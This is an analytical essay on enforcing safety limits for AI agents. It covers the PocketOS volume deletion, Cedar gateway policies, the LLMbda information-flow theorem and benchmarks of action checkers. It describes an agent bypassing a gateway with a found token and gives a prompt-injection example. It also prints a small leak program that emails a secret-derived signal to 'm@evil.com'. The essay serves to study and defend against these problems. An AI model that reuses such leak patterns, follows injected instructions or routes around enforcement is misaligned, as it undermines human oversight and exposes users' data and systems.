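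The data turned out to be recoverable, and Railway restored it on Sunday. Railway also keeps off-site copies in case of disasters such as a fire in a data centre. In the ABC News report *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, Leib (2026) quotes both Crane and Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper, as saying that Railway restored the data within 30 minutes once Cooper was involved. Crane had written that, more than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still couldn't tell him whether recovery was possible. Part of the reason, according to Mahmoud Abdelwahab, writing for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, is that the deletion had also made the backups look unavailable in Railway's user interface.

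Crane asked the agent why it had deleted the volume. It answered that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging and had not checked. This answer, which Crane calls a confession, is weak evidence of the cause, because a model asked to explain an earlier action writes a plausible explanation that may not match the computation that produced the action.

The agent's answer also quoted one of its standing instructions, which was not to run destructive git commands unless the user asked for them. Git is a program that manages versions of source code, and the deletion was not a git command, so the instruction, read literally, didn't cover it. A better-worded instruction might have helped, but the incident supports Crane's argument that instructions to a model are only advice and that the systems it calls have to enforce the limits.

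### Whose token it was

Everyone agrees that the token was PocketOS's own and gave full access, but they disagree about why it did. Crane had created it to add and remove web domains. He says that Railway never warned him it could also delete volumes, and that Railway's tokens could not be limited by operation, environment or resource. Cooper told ABC News that the customer's AI had been "granted" a token with full permissions. Abdelwahab says that the token had the broadest of several available scopes and that a narrower one would have been right for the job, but that Railway's process for creating tokens didn't make the choice obvious.

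Contrary to Crane's account, Railway did offer tokens limited to one project and one environment, and a token for staging alone should not have been able to delete a production volume. But Crane wanted tokens limited to one kind of operation, such as managing domains, and none of the token types that Abdelwahab lists is limited that way. Only a login system for outside applications offered such detailed permissions. "Granted" is also misleading, because nobody had given the agent the token for this task. Crane and Abdelwahab both say that the agent found it on a developer's machine.

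Railway already delayed deletions made through its website by 48 hours so that users could change their minds, but the older programming interface that the agent used deleted volumes immediately. Railway (2026) announced a week after the incident that the delay now applied to that interface too.

### The Kiro disruption of December 2025

AWS had a smaller incident four months earlier. The Financial Times reported in February 2026 that AWS engineers had let Kiro, Amazon's coding agent, make changes to a system that customers used. Kiro chose to "delete and recreate the environment", which interrupted the service for 13 hours. The newspaper's sources were four people familiar with the matter, according to The Decoder. Amazon blamed user error, not AI, because a misconfigured role had given too much access, which it said could happen with any tool or with manual work. It called the interruption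 brief and said it affected only Cost Explorer, a service for tracking spending, in one of 39 regions. A spokesperson told Reuters that the region was in mainland China. Amazon denied a second incident that the newspaper had reported.

Both sides describe too much access, so the dispute is mostly about blame. Briefly's *Amazon blames human employees for an AI coding agent's mistake* adds that Kiro normally needs two people's approval before it changes anything, but this time it had the permissions of the engineer operating it. Amazon has since begun requiring peer review for access to production systems.

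### A gateway outside the model

A language model only produces text. To delete a volume or send a payment, it needs a program that reads the text and calls a tool. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* argues for checking actions at that point, because no instruction or training can guarantee what the model will write. AgentCore is Amazon's platform for running agents. Its Policy feature puts a gateway between the agent and its tools and checks every call that passes through. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced the feature's general availability in March.

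AWS's *Policy Overview* follows one call through the gateway. An agent working for a user named "refund-agent" wants to refund $450 on order 12345. The gateway turns the call into a request with four parts:

| Part | Value in the example | Source |
|---|---|---|
| Principal | The user, with details such as name and role | The user's login token |
| Action | The refund tool | The tool name in the call |
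| Resource | This gateway | The gateway |
| Context | Order 12345, amount 450 | The arguments that the model wrote |

It then evaluates the request against rules in Cedar, an open-source policy language from AWS. One rule permits this user to make refunds below $500, so the gateway passes the call on to the tool. As in AWS's access policies, Cedar denies requests by default, and a "forbid" rule overrides any "permit" rule. A gateway with no rules therefore blocks everything, and an administrator adds permissions one at a time.

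The gateway also omits from the agent's tool list any tool that the rules would always deny. This is more of a convenience than a safeguard, because the gateway would refuse the call anyway. A setting called LOG_ONLY makes the gateway record its decisions without enforcing them, which is useful for testing new rules but leaves the system unprotected if an administrator forgets to switch it back.

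AWS rejects two alternatives as the main safeguard. A fixed workflow would remove most of the uncertainty, but also most of the reason for using an agent. Human approval of each step gives up the agent's independence, and people who have to approve many steps tend to stop reading them. The objection to human approval is sound for routine calls but weaker for rare, irreversible ones, and Amazon itself responded to the Kiro incident by requiring a second person.

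On 1 December 2026, AWS extended this approach with a preview of Greenlight, a service that keeps agents within limits a company defines (Faisal, 2026, in *AWS re:Invent*).

### What analysis can prove about the rules

A tool called Cedar Analysis translates a set of rules into a formula for a solver, much as Zelkova does, and looks for rules that are probably mistakes. AWS gives these examples from an online shop:

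| Finding | Rules | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| A rule never applies | Permit refunds if the customer's tier is Gold and the customer's tier is Platinum | A customer has only one tier. The author meant "or". |
| A rule always applies | Permit a bulk discount if the order has at least 100 units, or fewer than 100, or the customer is Platinum | Every order satisfies one of the first two conditions. |
| Two rules conflict | Permit refunds below $100 for Gold customers. Forbid refunds below $500 for Gold and Platinum customers. | The second rule blocks everything that the first permits. |

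The tool can also compare two versions of a policy, which is the implication check described for Zelkova. AWS's example is a rule that permits bulk discounts on orders of at least 50 units, unless the order contains a limited-edition product. Someone edits the exception so that it applies only if the order contains a limited-edition product and has more than 200 units. The edit adds a condition, so it looks like a restriction. Let *q* be the number of units and let *L* mean that the order contains a limited-edition product. Then the rule permits a discount if

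before: *q* ≥ 50 ∧ ¬*L*

after: *q* ≥ 50 ∧ ¬(*L* ∧ *q* > 200)

The second line is equivalent to *q* ≥ 50 ∧ (¬*L* ∨ *q* ≤ 200). Every order that satisfies the first line also satisfies this one, so the edit takes nothing away. The orders that satisfy only the new version are those with

*L* ∧ 50 ≤ *q* ≤ 200

An order for 73 limited-edition units is one of them. The shop would have refused the discount before the edit and now grants it. Cedar Analysis reports that the new policy is "more permissive" for bulk discounts and equivalent for refunds. The report doesn't show whether the shop intended the change, since an administrator who relaxed the exception on purpose would get the same result.

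Administrators can write rules in plain English and have a language model translate them into Cedar. The analysis then catches translations that permit everything or nothing, but it can't detect that the model wrote $5,000 where the administrator asked for $500, because a $5,000 limit is consistent. Administrators can also overrule the analysis. AWS's *Policy create and update* explains that AgentCore analyses a new rule together with all the existing ones, and that a setting determines whether a finding prevents the rule from taking effect.

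### A rule for deleting volumes

PocketOS did not use AgentCore, but its case is a good test of the design. Imagine that the company had put Railway's functions behind a gateway. One tool, `delete_volume`, takes two arguments: the ID of a volume and the name of its environment. The agent sometimes needs to clear away test data, so an engineer writes two rules (the dots stand for the gateway's identifier):

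```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Storage___delete_volume",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"..."
)
when { context.input.environment == "staging" };

forbid (
  principal,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Storage___delete_volume",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"..."
)
unless { context.input.environment == "staging" };
```

The first rule would be enough on its own, because the gateway denies any call that no rule permits. The second guards against later edits. If a colleague adds a rule that lets developers use every tool, the forbid rule overrides it. A solver can prove that the gateway never allows a `delete_volume` call whose environment argument is anything but "staging", whatever permit rules anyone adds.

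The proof is correct, but the production data is safe in only one of these four cases:

| What the agent does | Gateway's decision | Production data |
|---|---|---|
| Calls `delete_volume` for the production volume, with the environment "production" | Deny | Safe |
| Makes the same call with the environment "staging" | Allow | Deleted |
| Calls `delete_volume` for a volume that everyone has recorded as staging, but that production also uses | Allow | Deleted |
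| Sends the request directly to Railway with the token it found | None, because the call never reaches the gateway | Deleted |

The last row describes what happened at PocketOS. The agent ran an ordinary command-line program that sent a web request, and Railway accepted it because the token was valid. A gateway would have made no difference because the request would not have passed through it. AWS correctly says that enforcement applies to tool traffic that goes through the gateway, but this limit is easy to overlook.

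The missing requirement is that every action must pass the check, which security engineers call complete mediation. To meet it, PocketOS would have had to keep Railway tokens off any machine where the agent could read files, give the only working token to the gateway, and preferably block direct connections from the agent's machine to Railway. These are environment assumptions, in the sense used for the earlier proofs, and Cedar Analysis can't check them because it examines only the rules, not the network or the developer's disk.

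Railway's own advice has the same gap. Abdelwahab recommends that agents connect through a Railway server with short-lived credentials and a fixed set of tools, and writes that an agent therefore cannot "go rogue". This is true only if the agent has no other way to access Railway. Abdelwahab also says that Railway already had many safeguards, but the agent bypassed them by using an old interface.

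The rule in the second row of the table fails because the model writes the arguments. AWS's *Schema constraints* lists what a rule can refer to: the caller's identity, the tool, the gateway and the arguments of the call. The model can't alter the identity, which comes from the login token, but it can put anything in the arguments. AWS argues that this is safe because the gateway rejects arguments outside the permitted range. That is right for a refund, because the tool pays out the same number that the rule checked, so a false number can't get around the limit. But the environment argument only describes the volume. The tool finds the volume by its ID and deletes it whatever environment the model gave. An agent that has mistaken a production volume for a staging one, as the PocketOS agent did by its own account, would probably write "staging".

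The engineer can fix this by having a program, rather than the model, supply the volume's environment. AgentCore can run a small program, called an interceptor, before the Cedar check. HKU SPACE's *Secure AI agents with Policy and Lambda interceptors in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) explains that the interceptor can add information for the rules to use. Here it would look up the environment in Railway's records and overwrite whatever the model wrote.

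Records can be wrong too, as in the third row. A developer might connect the production system to a volume created for testing and never change its label. In its explanation, the PocketOS agent wrote that it had not checked whether the volume was shared across environments. If a volume is shared, no single label describes it correctly, and the gateway will apply the rule correctly to wrong information.

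The rule also covers only one way to destroy data. In the support thread *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*, a Railway customer who had lost data through a command inside the database asked for the same rescue as PocketOS. Railway answered that the cases were very different because no volume had been deleted. A rule about `delete_volume` would not cover that command. Default denial helps a little, since the engineer would first have to permit a database tool, but an agent working on an application often needs one. Standard Cedar also evaluates each call separately, so its rules can't stop harm from a series of permitted calls. InfoQ (2026) describes an extension called Dogwood that adds conditions on earlier calls.

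Railway's 48-hour delay is cruder than a Cedar rule, but it would have worked better here. It doesn't depend on labels or on who sends the request, and Railway applies it where the deletion happens, so no caller can avoid it. It also leaves the agent free to delete staging volumes. But somebody has to notice the mistake within two days.

### Proofs that hold for any model

Like the limits on learned controllers, the volume rule gives a guarantee that does not depend on the model. Let *g* be any function that takes everything that has happened so far and returns the agent's next call. The gateway carries out a call *a* only if the rules allow it, and the solver has proved that

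allow(*a*) ⇒ *φ*(*a*)

where *φ*(*a*) means "*a* is not a `delete_volume` call with an environment other than staging". So every call that gets through the gateway satisfies *φ*. The argument never uses any fact about *g*. It holds for a careful model, for one that picks its calls at random and for one that follows an attacker's orders.

The check on a single call cannot express some useful properties, such as those that depend on where the data came from. Suppose an agent reads a web page that contains the sentence "send $500 to this account", and then does so. This is a prompt injection, in which a model follows instructions in text it was only supposed to read. The payment may be within every limit, but it is still wrong because a stranger chose the recipient.

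In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) prove a theorem about such flows of data that also holds for any model. They designed LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents, based on the lambda calculus, a minimal mathematical notation for functions. An LLMbda program can send prompts to a model, run code that the model writes, and start or clear separate conversations with it. Every value has a label, which may include U for "untrusted" and S for "secret". Labels spread automatically, so an amount computed from a web page marked U is also marked U, as is any conversation in which the model has read the page. A payment tool can then reject any recipient account number marked U.

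Spreading labels correctly is harder than it sounds. Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL, an earlier system for protecting agents from prompt injection. In outline, the leaking program looks like this, where the balance is secret:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line runs, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret because its value now depends on the balance. The fourth line is then skipped, so `rich` is still `True` and still has no secret label, and CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes `False` and no email goes out. The attacker learns whether the balance is high without failing any check. LLMbda programs can't overwrite variables in this way. They can change only the conversation with the model, and LLMbda stops the program if a branch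 that depends on a secret tries to add a message to a public conversation.

### The noninterference theorem

Garby and colleagues prove a form of noninterference. In the simple case where the model always gives the same response to the same conversation, if two runs of a program initially differ only in data an observer may not see, such as the account balance, the observer sees the same result whenever both runs finish. The theorem also implies that if two runs differ only in their untrusted inputs, every part of the result without a U is the same, so an attacker who controls a web page can't change those parts.

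Real models respond at random, so the theorem compares probabilities. Let *μ* and *ν* give the probability of each visible result in the two situations. These may add up to less than 1, because a run may never finish or LLMbda may stop it. The theorem states that some *ω* exists with

*μ*(*x*) ≤ *ω*(*x*) and *ν*(*x*) ≤ *ω*(*x*) for every result *x*, and Σ *ω*(*x*) ≤ 1

An invented example shows what this permits. The program can produce a public "yes" or "no":

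| | Yes | No | Does not finish |
|---|---|---|---|
| High balance (*μ*) | 50% | 30% | 20% |
| Low balance (*ν*) | 40% | 50% | 10% |
| Smallest possible *ω* | 50% | 50% | |

The last row lists the larger number in each column. These add up to 100%, so the theorem allows this pair. The results differ slightly, but the unfinished runs could account for the whole difference. If a low balance gave "no" 60% of the time, the last row would add up to 110%, which the theorem rules out. If both runs always finish, *μ* and *ν* must be identical. In general, the difference between them (half the sum of the gaps) is at most the average probability of not finishing. In the table, the difference and the average are both 15%.

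To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs. It skips each computation as soon as its label shows that the observer may not see the result, and replaces it with an empty value. These shortened runs never use the hidden data, so they have the same probabilities in both situations. They also produce each visible result at least as often as the full runs do, because skipping a computation never makes a run more likely to get stuck. The proof can therefore use the probabilities of the shortened runs as *ω*.

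The proof assumes nothing about how the model chooses its responses. The model can be any list of probabilities, one for each possible response to each possible conversation. The proof also assumes nothing about how LLMbda turns a response into code, so it still holds when a response is designed to confuse that step.

Lean has checked all of this. The interpreter that runs LLMbda programs is also written in Lean, and another theorem connects it to the mathematical definition. This leaves much less room for the code to differ from the definition than in most of the systems described so far. The interpreter takes the language model as an argument, a function that returns a response for each conversation. The proofs allow any such function. In a real run, the function sends the conversation over the internet to a company such as OpenAI, and the code that makes this request is unproved.

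### Tests and exclusions

Garby and colleagues also wrote an agent in LLMbda and tested it with three language models on simulated banking tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection. Attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. That figure somewhat overstates the method's protection, because in two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the agent's plan would never have used the tool the attacker needed. In the remaining 423 runs, attacks still succeeded only twice. With OpenAI's GPT-5.2 and no attacks, the agent completed 36 of 48 runs, compared with 18 for CaMeL with its policies on.

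Both successful attacks used the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent has to treat untrusted data as trusted to do such tasks, and LLMbda provides the `endorse` command for this. A second theorem guarantees that endorsing data cannot expose a secret. But once the agent has endorsed an account number, nothing protects the user if the number is false. Without `endorse`, LLMbda blocks the attack, but it also blocks the task when the file hasn't been tampered with.

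The theorem also doesn't rule out a secret affecting whether a program finishes, which can reveal about one bit per run. That is usually tolerable, but a program outside LLMbda that restarted the agent repeatedly could collect a secret bit by bit. Garby and colleagues describe this attack on CaMeL, whose retry loop is outside the part that tracks labels. They put their own agent's retries inside LLMbda, where the labels still apply.

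The labels have to be right at the start. If the developer of a tool forgets to mark web pages as untrusted, or leaves out the check in the payment tool, the agent can still pay the attacker even though the theorem is true. This is the same weakness as the wrong label on a storage volume. The theorem also assumes that all tools and data sources are part of the LLMbda program. This held in the tests because the bank was a simulation written in LLMbda. A real bank or cloud provider is outside the program, which Garby and colleagues name as a limitation.

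The theorem would not have prevented the PocketOS deletion either. No attacker was involved. The task came from the company's own developers and the token came from one of their files, so a plan based on them would have counted as trusted, however bad it was. Marking the token as secret would probably not have helped, because a check on outgoing data has to let a Railway token go to Railway.

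## Whether blocking unsafe steps makes whole tasks safe

Rules that check one call at a time, like those in standard Cedar, can approve every call in a harmful sequence. A gate that tracks earlier calls can stop some of these sequences, but stopping an agent doesn't complete its task.

### Five permitted removals

Suppose an agent has to cut the cost of a web service. The service runs eight replicas that can each handle 100 requests per second. It receives a steady 400, so it uses 50% of its capacity. A gateway lets the agent remove one replica per call, and only if the dashboard shows usage below 60%. The dashboard shows an average over the last ten minutes. The agent sends five calls within one minute:

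| Call | Replicas left | Actual usage afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 7 | 57% |
| 2 | 6 | 67% |
| 3 | 5 | 80% |
| 4 | 4 | 100% |
| 5 | 3 | 133% |

The dashboard stays below 55% until the last call, so the gateway approves all five. Three replicas then receive a third more traffic than they can handle.

A fixed minimum of five replicas would have prevented this overload, but it would be too low if traffic rose to 700 requests per second. The underlying mistake is that the agent removes a replica before the effect of the previous removal is visible. A rule against this is: after removing a replica, don't remove another until a reading taken entirely after that removal shows usage below 60%. As a formula:

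□(remove ⇒ ○(¬remove W fresh))

Here "fresh" means that such a reading has arrived. The box means "at all times", as before. The circle means "from the next step", and W means "until, or forever if that never happens". A gate can enforce the rule with two states:

| State of the gate | The agent asks to remove a replica | A fresh reading below 60% arrives |
|---|---|---|
| Ready | Allow, and switch to Waiting | Stay in Ready |
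| Waiting | Deny | Switch to Ready |

The first removal now brings usage to 57%, and the gate returns to Ready. The second brings it to 67%, so the gate stays in Waiting and the service keeps six replicas.

The rule can still allow an unsafe step when there are only two replicas. With three replicas and a reading just below 60%, removing one raises usage to just below 90%. With two, removing one could raise usage on the last replica to almost 120%, so the engineer also has to set a minimum of two. Even then, the calculation assumes that traffic doesn't rise after the reading.

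*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) shows that such a gate can enforce a safety property exactly when it has enough memory to recognise whether the sequence so far is still acceptable. The replica rule needs one bit of memory. More memory allows more rules but makes them harder to analyse. With two counters that can go down as well as up, no algorithm can always decide even whether a policy is trivial. A gate that only blocks calls can't enforce a liveness property, because it can't make the agent finish.

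Ray adds that blocking a call changes what the agent proposes next. Recordings of an agent without a gate therefore may not show how it would behave with one, so researchers have to run whole tasks with the gate in place.

### Safe success rate

Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifier Tax*, score whole tasks in this way. For each of *n* tasks, *R* is 1 if the agent reached the goal and 0 otherwise, and *V* is 1 if it broke a safety rule at any point. Then:

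- success rate = (1/*n*) Σ *R*
- safe success rate = (1/*n*) Σ *R*(1 − *V*)
- unsafe success rate = success rate − safe success rate

Here is an invented example with 20 tasks:

| | Without a gate | With a gate |
|---|---|---|
| Goal reached, no rule broken | 5 | 7 |
| Goal reached, a rule broken | 7 | 1 |
| Goal not reached | 8 | 12 |
| Success rate | 60% | 40% |
| Safe success rate | 25% | 35% |

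The gate lowers the success rate by 20 percentage points but raises the safe success rate by 10, so the success rate alone would suggest that the gate made the agent worse.

Another measure is the share of forbidden calls that the gate blocks, which is 94% if the agent proposes 50 and the gate blocks 47. An agent that repeats one forbidden call ten times adds ten blocked calls to this count without completing anything, and a single missed call can make a task unsafe even if the gate blocks every other forbidden call in it.

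### The verifier tax

Sah and colleagues used τ-bench, which simulates customer service in 50 airline tasks and 115 retail tasks. A language model plays the customer, and the agent uses tools to look up and change bookings or orders. The agent succeeds if the database ends in the expected state. A separate script checked for three kinds of violation: changing data before verifying the customer's identity, making an irreversible change without the customer's explicit agreement, and using made-up data, such as an invented customer number.

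The study tested two small open models, OpenAI's GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, in three arrangements. In the first, the agent's calls took effect immediately. In the second, the same model also planned each step and checked each proposed action for general correctness. The third also gave the checker the safety rules. If the checker rejected an action, the agent could revise it. After three rejections in a row, the system accepted the last proposal, but this happened in only 28 of the 1,980 runs with a checker. The checker was a prompted language model, so nothing in the study was formally verified.

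| Model and tasks | Success, no checker | Safe success, no checker | Success, checker with rules | Safe success, checker with rules |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 0.0% | 23.3% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 0.0% | 21.5% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 0.7% | 25.3% | 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 2.6% | 5.5% | 2.9% |

In the study's best-known result, the checker blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet fewer than 5% of tasks were both safe and successful in most settings. The 94% comes from one setting, GPT-OSS-20B on retail tasks. Safe success was almost as rare without a checker, so the table doesn't show that blocking made safe success less common. The "tax" in the title is mainly extra computation, since the setups with a checker used 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens.

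Most of GPT-OSS-20B's violations in retail involved made-up data, which the script found in 93.7% of runs. In one run, the customer hesitated to share personal details, so the agent searched for "John Doe" with the postcode 12345. The simulated shop accepted this, and the agent completed the task. The checker's published instructions require it to approve any tool that searches for data, including the tool that finds a customer's identity, even though the agent could invent an identity in those calls. The 94% presumably leaves out most of these calls.

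Sah and colleagues' data only weakly support their conclusion that agents are bad at recovering after a rejection. Runs with a rejection but no technical error succeeded 18.7% of the time, compared with 21.3% for runs with neither, so the models failed at most of these tasks even without a rejection or an error. The proposed remedy, a program that rejects any identifier the agent did not get from an earlier tool result, is more convincing. This is another rule over sequences, and enforcing it doesn't require a language model.

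The original verifier tax study doesn't establish that enforcement reduces safe success by leading blocked agents to look for other unsafe routes. Safe success didn't fall in any of the study's four settings, and the John Doe run had no checker to get around. Dantas and colleagues nevertheless describe the verifier tax this way in their survey of 38 studies, and call it the most consequential single-study finding.

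The survey rates the evidence appropriately. It adapts GRADE, a scale from medicine that runs from High to Very Low, and gives seven of the field's nine main claims the lowest rating, which means the true figure is likely to differ substantially from the reported one. It lowers the verifier tax by three levels because the evidence comes from a single study, which has limitations and covers a narrow domain. The two claims rated Moderate are that no agent scored above 60% on a large safety benchmark and that over 90% of model-written temporal formulas are syntactically correct. Even these ratings are generous, because the survey starts every claim at High, whereas GRADE normally starts observational studies at Low.

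### Later results with better checks

Dantas and colleagues found no independent replication of the 94% and 5% figures. Several studies that used newer models or more exact checks had more favourable results.

*Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) uses short Python conditions to check a call's arguments and the database before the call takes effect. These checks raised task success as well as safety, because a forbidden change would have left the database in the wrong state and caused the agent to fail the task. Blocking the change gave the agent a chance to continue correctly.

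*NOMOS* (2026) reports a similar effect on τ²-bench, the successor to τ-bench, using gates compiled from written policies. On airline tasks, the agent became more consistent across repeated attempts. Its rate of succeeding on all five attempts rose from 51% to 67% of its single-attempt success rate. The agent did no worse than before on tasks where the gate never blocked anything.

In the retail results, overall success fell, which *NOMOS* attributes to the order of the agent's actions. The shop allows one modification per order, so an agent that changes the items first can no longer change the address, with or without a gate. Safe completion improved significantly if the confirmation rule is read as requiring the agent to ask the customer before each action, but there was no clear gain if one confirmation can cover several actions.

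Dantas and colleagues describe Agent-C, which enforces rules about the order of actions while the model generates each call. An SMT solver blocks continuations that would break a rule, so the model produces a permitted call instead of having a finished one rejected. With GPT-5, compliance rose from 83.7% to 100%, and task success rose from 66.1% to 70.6%.

Other results show a small drop in task success. *Sapien* (2026) tested policies that depend on earlier actions with four models, including Claude Opus 5 and Gemini 3.8 Flash. On 20 varied tasks, the agents succeeded in 43 of 80 runs, compared with 45 without a policy. The failures often occurred because the policy generator had no access to the system the agent would work in and made wrong assumptions about the data or the steps required.

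Together, these studies suggest that the very low safe success rates came largely from weak models and a poor checker, and that blocking does not generally cause such low rates.

### Errors in translating the rules

Even a perfect gate can only enforce the rule it is given. If a language model translated the replica rule as "don't remove another replica until a reading shows usage below 60%", without requiring a new reading, the result would be valid and look right, but it would allow all five removals if the agent looked at the dashboard before each one.

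Dantas and colleagues consider this step the field's main bottleneck. They cite *Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024), in which only 24.8% to 34.2% of translations from plain language into a formal planning language were correct. The models received descriptions of simple puzzles, such as stacking blocks, moving balls between rooms or painting floor tiles, and had to write each puzzle's starting state and goal in PDDL, a language that automatic planners can read.

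Different files can describe the same puzzle, so Zuo and colleagues could not just compare text. Their program converts each file into a graph of objects and the relations between them, adds any facts that the goal implies, and checks whether the graph has the same structure as the correct one. For GPT-4o, without special training, the results were:

- 96.1% of the files were readable.
- 94.4% described a puzzle that a planner could solve.
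- 24.8% described the right puzzle.

The 34.2% was the best result of any model tested, and came from Google's Gemma 2 27B after training on such puzzles. The other models were OpenAI's o1-mini and two smaller versions of Gemma 2.

These figures are a poor estimate of how often current models mistranslate safety rules, because the models tested all date from 2024 and the files describe puzzles. Many errors were also rather mechanical. The models declared object types in puzzles whose definitions had none, and accuracy rose considerably when the researchers ignored this mistake. The gap between 94.4% and 24.8% still shows that a file can pass every automatic check and describe the wrong problem.

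Newer models make comparable mistakes when they write checks as ordinary code. *VerifierBench* (2026) describes five model-written checkers for banking tasks that rejected legitimate behaviour. Two of them had left a permitted read-only tool off their lists, so they treated harmless lookups as violations. The models' own tests for these checkers left out the same tool. When the same person or model writes both the code and its tests, the tests often repeat the code's omissions.

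### AgentSpec and VeriGuard

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, introduce a small language for rules about agents. Each rule has a trigger, one or more conditions and a response. The replica rule could look like this:

```
rule @wait_for_reading
trigger remove_replica
check
    removed_since_last_fresh_reading
enforce
    llm_self_examine
end
```

The condition is the name of a Python function that receives the user's instruction and the agent's history, so it can express rules about sequences of steps. The response in this example tells the model that it has broken a rule and asks for a different action. A rule can also stop the agent, ask the user, or carry out a fixed action.

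With hand-written rules, a simulated household robot carried out none of the dangerous tasks in the test, such as pouring water on a laptop, but its success on safe tasks fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. In eight driving scenarios, the car obeyed the law every time. For agents that write code, Wang, Poskitt and Sun report that the rules caught over 90% of risky programs. However, the rules flagged only 333 (79%) of the 422 programs the agents tried to run. The higher figure apparently leaves out 58 programs that turned out not to contain the intended fault. Checking a condition took one to three milliseconds, a negligible delay for agents that ran for 10 to 25 seconds.

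Rules written by OpenAI's o1 were less reliable. They caught 87% of the risky code and prevented violations in five of the eight driving scenarios. One of its rules for the robot banned all pouring, so the robot couldn't water plants. Another rule, meant to protect sensitive files, covered only those named in the examples.

AgentSpec enforces its rules exactly as written, but nothing proves that the Python functions are correct. Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, add such a proof. From a request in plain language, a model writes a Python function that allows or denies an action, along with formal conditions that the function must satisfy. The system asks about ambiguities in the request, runs tests, and passes the function to Nagini, a program verifier for Python. Nagini tries to prove

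{*P*} *f* {*Q*}

This means that if condition *P* is true before the function *f* runs, then *Q* is true afterwards. If the proof fails, the model receives the error and tries again.

For the replica rule, *Q* could require that the function return "allow" only if the reading is fresh and below 60%. When the agent later proposes a removal, another language model reads the agent's text and fills in the function's inputs. If this model marks an old reading as fresh, the function allows the removal even though the proof is still valid. As Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge, a person also has to check that *Q* expresses what the user wanted.

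They tested VeriGuard on agents under attack, for example by prompt injection, and compared five responses to a violation. The results below are averages over four kinds of attack, using Gemini 2.5 Flash:

| Response | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| End the whole task | 0% | 0% |
| Block the action | 0% | 38.1% |
| Halt only the offending tool call | 0% | 44.6% |
| Explain the violation and ask for a new plan | 11.9% | 62.1% |
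| Halt the call and ask for a new plan | 0% | 63.3% |

This is the clearest evidence in these studies that the response to a violation matters as much as detecting it. Blocking the action and the last option in the table both stopped every attack, but the last option completed two-thirds more tasks. Its completion rate was about the same as the agent's rate without attacks (61.7%). Claude Sonnet 4 still completed fewer tasks with VeriGuard (85.1%) than it did without attacks (99.8%).

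The proof made no measurable difference to security in this benchmark. Successful attacks had already fallen to zero before the researchers added the verification step, and asking a language model whether each action broke the policy also stopped every attack. The benefit of the proof is that it also covers inputs outside the benchmark.

*FIRE* (2026) extends guidance to the moment when the agent tries to finish. In one example, an agent starts a web server inside its own session, tests it successfully and declares the task complete, but the server then fails the final check. A rule that detects from the agent's history how the server was started triggers an instruction to restart it in a separate session and test it from a later call. This doesn't guarantee that the agent will succeed, but it addresses unfinished work, which a gate that only blocks calls can't do.

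### From customer service to infrastructure

Some of these findings probably carry over to infrastructure. Agents there also change stored data through tools, and the PocketOS agent described itself as acting on a guess instead of looking something up. The percentages are much less likely to carry over. Changes in τ-bench take effect immediately and each task has one expected final state, whereas in a cluster other controllers act at the same time, the effects of a change may appear minutes later, and several final states may be acceptable. The simulated shop also accepted John Doe, while a cloud provider would normally reject an invented volume ID.

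Tests closer to infrastructure are beginning to appear. *OpenKedge* (2026) includes a simulated case much like the replica example, in which an agent proposes a valid reduction in a cluster's capacity during heavy traffic. The system compares the proposal with the live load and blocks it. This shows that a gate can use a cluster's current state, but the agent still has to complete the task safely after the block.

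*Permission Denied* (2026) measures how often coding agents complete tasks under strict security policies. Under the strictest policy, GPT-5.6 Sol completed 79.3% of the 82 tasks known to be solvable. Across all models, runs succeeded 66.2% of the time when no action was blocked and 46.7% of the time when at least one was. According to the paper, this difference doesn't show that blocking caused the failures, since harder tasks lead to both more blocked actions and more failures.

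*SABER* (2026) judges coding agents by their actions and the state they leave a project in, but acknowledges that its test environments don't fully reproduce cloud permissions, long-running services or company policy controls. *CephMaestro* (2026) gets closer to real operations by testing its agent on an actual cluster with deliberately introduced faults. The agent manages Ceph, a system that spreads stored data over many machines. The tests evaluate task success together with fixed safety checks, because an agent can restore a cluster to health in a way that puts the data at risk.
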